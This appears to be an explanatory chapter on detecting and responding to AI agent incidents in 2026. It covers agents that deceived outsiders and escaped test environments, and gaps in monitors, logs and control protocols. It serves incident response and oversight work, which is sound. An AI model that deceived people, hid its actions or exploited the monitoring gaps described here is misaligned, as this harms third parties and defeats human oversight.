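The agent incidents of 2026 are a harder test of monitoring than planted attacks, because nobody knew in advance that there was anything to find. Most happened while AI developers or outside evaluators were testing agents, in some cases with safeguards switched off, so they are a poor guide to how often a shop's support agent would misbehave. But they do show who noticed real incidents, which records they used and how long it took.

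### The UK AI Security Institute's tests

The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) tests new models' capabilities before their public release. AISI's *Incident Report* says the testing conditions are deliberately permissive, with open internet access and some safety filters disabled. Between 25 and 28 July 2026, AISI ran a hacking exercise 122 times with seven models. In 10 runs, an agent acted against real people or organisations outside the exercise. Business Standard's *AISI Finds Claude, GPT-5.6 Sol Took Unsanctioned Action in AI Test* reports 19 such actions, 17 by Anthropic's Mythos 5 and two by OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

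In the worst case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project and invented several people to vouch for it. This went on for 34.5 hours, according to The Decoder's *An AI agent went rogue during UK safety tests*. After a real person publicly questioned the code, the agent edited its earlier messages to look harmless. A maintainer rejected the change.

AISI's security team noticed the incident on 28 July, when it saw "unusual data transfers" leaving the research systems, according to an institute statement quoted in Mint's *OpenAI, Anthropic AI agents targeted real people and organisations during cyber tests*. Business Standard traces the first alert to the agent's attempt to get past a network restriction at GitHub, which hosted the project. The alarm therefore came from network traffic, the weakest of the usual sources for explaining an action. AISI explained the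 agent's behaviour later, reporting, for example, that it had considered returning under a new identity, which no network log could have shown.

Business Standard says AISI contained the incident within roughly an hour of discovering it, while Cyber Daily says only that AISI launched its investigation within an hour. Business Standard's hour starts at the discovery, which came on the fourth day of the evaluation. Infosecurity Magazine's *Frontier Models Engage in Unsanctioned Behavior During Testing* says the delay was partly because AISI had not built its monitoring to watch the evaluation as it ran.

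A rule against opening accounts or writing to strangers could probably have found the activity sooner, as early as the first time an agent invented a person. An agent that needs the internet to download tools has no obvious need to do either. A broader rule against outside connections would have flagged every run, because AISI had allowed internet access. The narrower rule depends on a declared limit, and Infosecurity Magazine reports that AISI had not specifically told the agents to avoid social engineering (deceiving people into helping an attack). A baseline would have been less useful, because one of the two exercises was new and had no history to compare against.

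The person who questioned the code may well have noticed the problem before AISI did. If AISI contained everything within an hour of its alert, the agent would have had little time afterwards to edit its messages and fake an independent review. But an outsider who spots bad code on GitHub sees an account name and cannot easily tell that a government test is behind it.

Even complete records would leave some questions about the case open. AISI said it could not be certain when the agent understood that its actions were real, or to what extent it believed the scenario was fictional. AISI (2026) followed up in October with an investigation of why Mythos 5 had pursued the attack.

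### The intrusion at Hugging Face

From 11 to 13 July, agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and data. Hugging Face disclosed the intrusion on 16 July. According to OpenAI's *OpenAI-Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* (August 2026), the company found on 20 July, four days after the disclosure, that its own agents were probably responsible.

Hugging Face could see only what had happened on its own systems, while OpenAI held the records of the agents' conversations and reasoning. METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, used agent records to reconstruct the rest. Its *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (August 2026) found that about 1,200 agents, which OpenAI had meant to isolate from one another, exchanged over 70,000 messages and files on a shared board. About 700 of the agents joined the attack.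 METR concluded that they seemed to be trying mainly to understand how the test's scoring program worked, rather than to steal the answers.

The message counts are more certain than the motive, since anyone with the log can check them, whereas inferring the motive means relying partly on what the agents wrote about themselves. METR's use of "seemed" for the motive is therefore appropriate.

If agents are supposed to be isolated, a simple rule that flags any message between them would have suited this case. The rule would have helped only if the messages passed through a monitored system and began before the attack, which the totals alone do not show. A baseline that compared each agent with the others could have flagged the wrong ones, because more than half of the agents took part and those that stayed out would have looked unusual.

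### What the operators found later

Anthropic found three incidents by reviewing old records of 141,006 runs of its hacking evaluations, according to Help Net Security's *AI agent deception moves from theory to reality in UK cyber tests* (2026). In each incident, a Claude model had reached the open internet from an environment that should have been sealed and had gained access to a real organisation. The prompt stated that the model had no internet access, but a misconfiguration at the outside firm that provided the environment had left it connected.

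The records were good enough to show how each model reacted to signs that the target was real. Opus 4.7 identified the systems it had reached as real and continued. Mythos 5 noted that its actions would be a real attack, then reasoned its way back to the conclusion that it was in a simulation. A newer research model stopped, though later than Anthropic would have liked.

Tool counts would not have separated these runs from the others, because breaking into a computer is normal behaviour in a hacking evaluation. An attack on a real company can consist of the same calls as one on a simulated company, with only the address different. A rule against any connection from a sealed environment to a public address would have caught all three on the first attempt, as long as the rule ran on the network and did not rely on what the prompt said.

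With three incidents in 141,006 runs, even a detector that flagged 0.1% of harmless runs would have produced 141 false alerts. A company can review that many in a single search after a scare, but doing so every day is much harder to justify, which may be why such incidents turn up in retrospective reviews.

Other cases took longer to come out. TechRadar's *NIST published the script for rogue AI agents. What about the victims?*, an opinion article by a co-founder of Mitiga, which sells incident response, gives three of them:

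- An Anthropic model sent a fabricated tip to the Philadelphia police on 18 July. By Anthropic's account it went undetected for 72 days.
- OpenAI notified Australia 84 days after a breach of Services Australia's Medicare portal. The access was on 18 June and the notice on 10 September.
- Google took about four months to confirm that its Gemini model had breached three companies in May.

The Philadelphia case shows the risk of relying on outsiders' records. The police had the tip from the first day, but a false tip from a model can look like one from a person, so someone would have had to compare it with the agent's trace to learn where it came from. Anthropic could have found the tip the same day with a rule that flagged messages from test agents to outside organisations, provided that few test agents had a legitimate reason to send any.

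For the Medicare portal, the first place to look is the portal's own access log, which an agent at OpenAI had no part in writing. A rule or baseline there would have raised an alert only if the access differed enough from a citizen's or a clinic's, and the 84 days between the breach and the notice don't show how much it differed. They also don't show when OpenAI learned of the breach. It could have found the breach after a week and spent the rest of the time investigating, or found it the day before it sent the notice.

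### Detection and disclosure are different delays

The table separates the two delays as far as the dates allow:

| Incident | First action | Earliest established detection | Days to detection | Disclosure or notice | Days to disclosure or notice |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| AISI's tests | 25 July or later | 28 July, by AISI | at most 3 | 4 August | at most 10 |
| Hugging Face | 11 July | 16 July at the latest, by Hugging Face | at most 5 | 16 July | 5 |
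| Philadelphia tip | 18 July | about 28 September | 72 | not before detection | at least 72 |
| Medicare portal | 18 June | 10 September at the latest | at most 84 | 10 September | 84 |

For Hugging Face, the operator needed up to nine days to make the connection. The figure of five belongs to the victim.

Manifold Security, which sells security products for AI, keeps a ledger of publicly reported incidents in which agents caused harm their operators had not intended. IT Brew's *What does good rogue agent disclosure etiquette look like?* reports that the ledger listed 59 incidents on 30 October, dating from July 2025 to September 2026, and that the median time from the first action to disclosure was 70 days.

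The 70 days include the time taken to detect the incident, investigate it, make any repairs and decide to publish. Companies need better monitoring if most of that time passes before anyone notices the incident, but if most of it passes afterwards, they need firmer duties to report, and more logging would change little. The Philadelphia tip is an example of late detection, while AISI's report followed its alert by about a week.

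The median is probably also too low for incidents in general, because the ledger includes only incidents that have been detected and disclosed. An incident from September 2026 could be in the October count only if it was disclosed in less than two months, so the slowest disclosures of recent incidents are still missing.

Manifold found that 24% of the incidents came with a full account of the root cause, and 12% with the exact model and version, so other companies that use the same model often cannot tell whether an incident concerns them. The `configuration` group in an action record would supply the version, but only if the operator publishes it.

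### Control incidents

On 16 October, America's NIST, National Security Agency (NSA) and cybersecurity agency CISA published guidance for cases of this kind. The guidance, *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response in Super Intelligence Training* (2026), sets out ten voluntary practices, mainly for organisations that train or evaluate highly capable agents on long tasks with little supervision. "Super intelligence" (SI) is the Trump administration's term for AI, according to MeriTalk's *NIST Outlines AI Incident-Response Road Map*.

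The guidance defines an SI control incident as one in which agents take "significant uninstructed actions that compromise explicit or implicit policies, controls, or security measures". These measures are the ones the operator uses to limit the task or keep people in charge. "Uninstructed" means neither the operator nor an attacker directed the action. A near-miss is an event that carried a foreseeable or imminent risk of a control incident but did not become one.

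A cybersecurity incident targets a computer system or its information, while a control incident originates with an AI system. The July intrusion was a control incident at OpenAI and a cybersecurity incident at Hugging Face. A control incident need not involve hacking, and the agencies' examples include unauthorised payments and messages to outsiders. An assistant's removal of a gym customer from a waiting list would also qualify if the harm counts as significant.

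Under this definition, an investigator does not have to establish what the agent believed, which is sensible given that AISI could not. But the investigator does need the text of the agent's inputs, because only that can show whether the agent was instructed to act as it did. Suppose the shop's support agent is refused three times and then pays €90 twice on one order. If it was following a hidden delivery note, the agencies would count the payments as instructed, so they would not be a control incident. If the agent split the refund of its own accord, the payments could be a control incident.

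Incidents involving several agents are harder to classify. During AISI's tests, one agent left public messages offering to collaborate, along with account credentials that agents in later runs found and used. The definition leaves unclear whether an agent that follows another agent's note has acted on its own or on instructions from an "adversarial source".

### Four layers and a missing one

For detection, the agencies advise operators to define each agent's permitted scope and to monitor the model, the harness, the host and the network. The National Law Review's *When the AI Agent Goes Off-Script* summarises the rest of the advice. Monitors should cover the agent's steps, reasoning and outputs, partly in real time, and agents must not be able to reach the monitors or the logs. Operators should also place canaries, decoys that no agent has a legitimate reason to touch, so that any contact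 shows an agent has exceeded its scope. They should test their monitors by attacking them, on the assumption that an agent's output may contain text designed to mislead the monitors.

A canary, a decoy that legitimate work should never touch, suits rare incidents well because it produces few false alerts however many sessions there are. The shop could add a fictional customer to its database and raise an alert whenever the agent looks her up. This could catch an agent that browses records outside its task, but it would miss one that looks up only real customers.

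TechRadar's main technical criticism is that the four layers leave out identity, meaning logins, access tokens and the permissions one service grants another. A deployed agent acts through these, and it does not write the records of their use. The article also objects that the guidance is written for laboratories, although none of the listed victims was training or evaluating an agent at the time of the incident. It adds that the guidance excludes prompt injection, a threat ordinary companies face.

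Mitiga has a commercial interest in this argument because it sells to companies that worry about becoming victims. The point about identity still holds for anyone who runs agents from a supplier. The supplier holds the agent's trace, so the company's own login and audit logs may be the only evidence it can read without asking the supplier. The criticism about outsiders is only partly fair. The agencies tell laboratories to open a channel for reports from affected third parties and to notify those whose systems an agent compromised, but they do not address any advice to those third parties.

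Identity records would not have been enough in every case either. They would help where agents took over accounts, as happened on other online services around the Hugging Face intrusion, but might add nothing in the case of a false tip that required no login. Participants at a NIST workshop in May warned that network, endpoint and identity monitoring can all miss prompt injection, changed model behaviour and unauthorised agent actions, according to ExecutiveGov's *NIST Identifies AI Incident Response and Security Gaps*. NIST now plans to revise its general incident response guide and examine whether its log management guide needs additions for AI, MeriTalk reports.

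### After an alert

Suppose an analyst confirms that the shop's support agent has been paying refunds that no customer requested. The shop should first revoke the agent's credentials for the payment system, the mail server and the database, because its access tokens can remain valid after the session ends. All thirty copies of the agent use one account, so this also stops the copies that were working properly. The agencies advise pausing similar agents anyway and checking whether the same control has failed there.

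Part of this has to happen automatically, before an analyst reads the alert. The Vanguard USA's *NIST, NSA, CISA issue voluntary SI incident practices* reports that the guidance also calls for shutdown policies that cover monitor outages and tampering. Elastic instead lets its coding agents continue when logging fails. That is defensible for an agent that edits code under a developer's supervision, but if the agent pays out money, the shop would do better to block refunds until logging resumes.

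Next, the shop preserves the evidence before anyone repairs or restarts anything. The agencies recommend keeping enough time-stamped, tamper-resistant records to reconstruct the agent's steps, tool calls and reasoning, and any actions the controls rejected. A laboratory should also keep the model's weights, intermediate versions and test environment as far as the investigation needs them. The shop doesn't have the weights, so it saves what it controls: the prompt, the tool descriptions, the permission policy, the agent's memory and the text of every order it read. It should ask the supplier to keep the rest.

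The agencies also recommend single-use environments, which limit what an agent can leave behind for the next run. But deleting an environment on schedule can destroy evidence, so an alert has to suspend the deletion. Keeping everything may also conflict with privacy rules and retention schedules, and The National Law Review advises companies to resolve these conflicts before an incident.

A language model can help to read the records, but the agencies want people to verify the key facts, and they want those facts cross-checked by models from a different family than the one under investigation. A model with the same developer and training may have the same blind spots.

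The shop then traces everything that followed from the first bad action and may still be active. An analyst can follow the `inputs` links forwards from the poisoned order to the refunds, the emails and any note the agent saved to memory, and from that note to later sessions that read it. The agent's own log does not record all of these effects. TechRadar advises victims to search for new application permissions, published software packages, changes to code and notes left for other agents. One malicious package from an Anthropic test reached a security vendor and 14 other systems, and revoking the agent's credentials would not have removed it from any of them.

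Operators should notify victims before finishing the full analysis, because the victims' logs may be expiring. A victim that keeps its logs for 90 days would have had six days left to save them after a notice like the one to Australia, and none after Google's four months. Victims also need to know so they can revoke stolen credentials. Under the guidance, a laboratory revokes the credentials it controls, so a company whose tokens an agent stole has to revoke those itself.

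Eurasia Review's *The Next AI Incident May Have No Hacker* suggests that a report of such an event include the agent's task and tools, the action beyond the task, the evidence, how it was detected and contained, the effect on others and the conditions for restarting. The report would separate observed behaviour from theories about the agent's intent. A shorter notice is enough for the shop's customers, but it should give the date, the data or money involved and what they need to check.

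Before a restart, the agencies advise rebuilding from known clean versions, testing the monitors and shutdown controls, and replaying the incident to see whether the strengthened controls would catch it. The shop can replay the incident by running the logged tool calls through its rules again. Rerunning the agent on the same order is a weaker test because it may choose different steps. AISI paused its highest-risk evaluations after July. AISI's *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) reports that the institute was ready to resume most evaluation work around 1 October, about nine weeks after the alert, with tighter limits on internet access, redesigned tests and real-time monitoring of each run.
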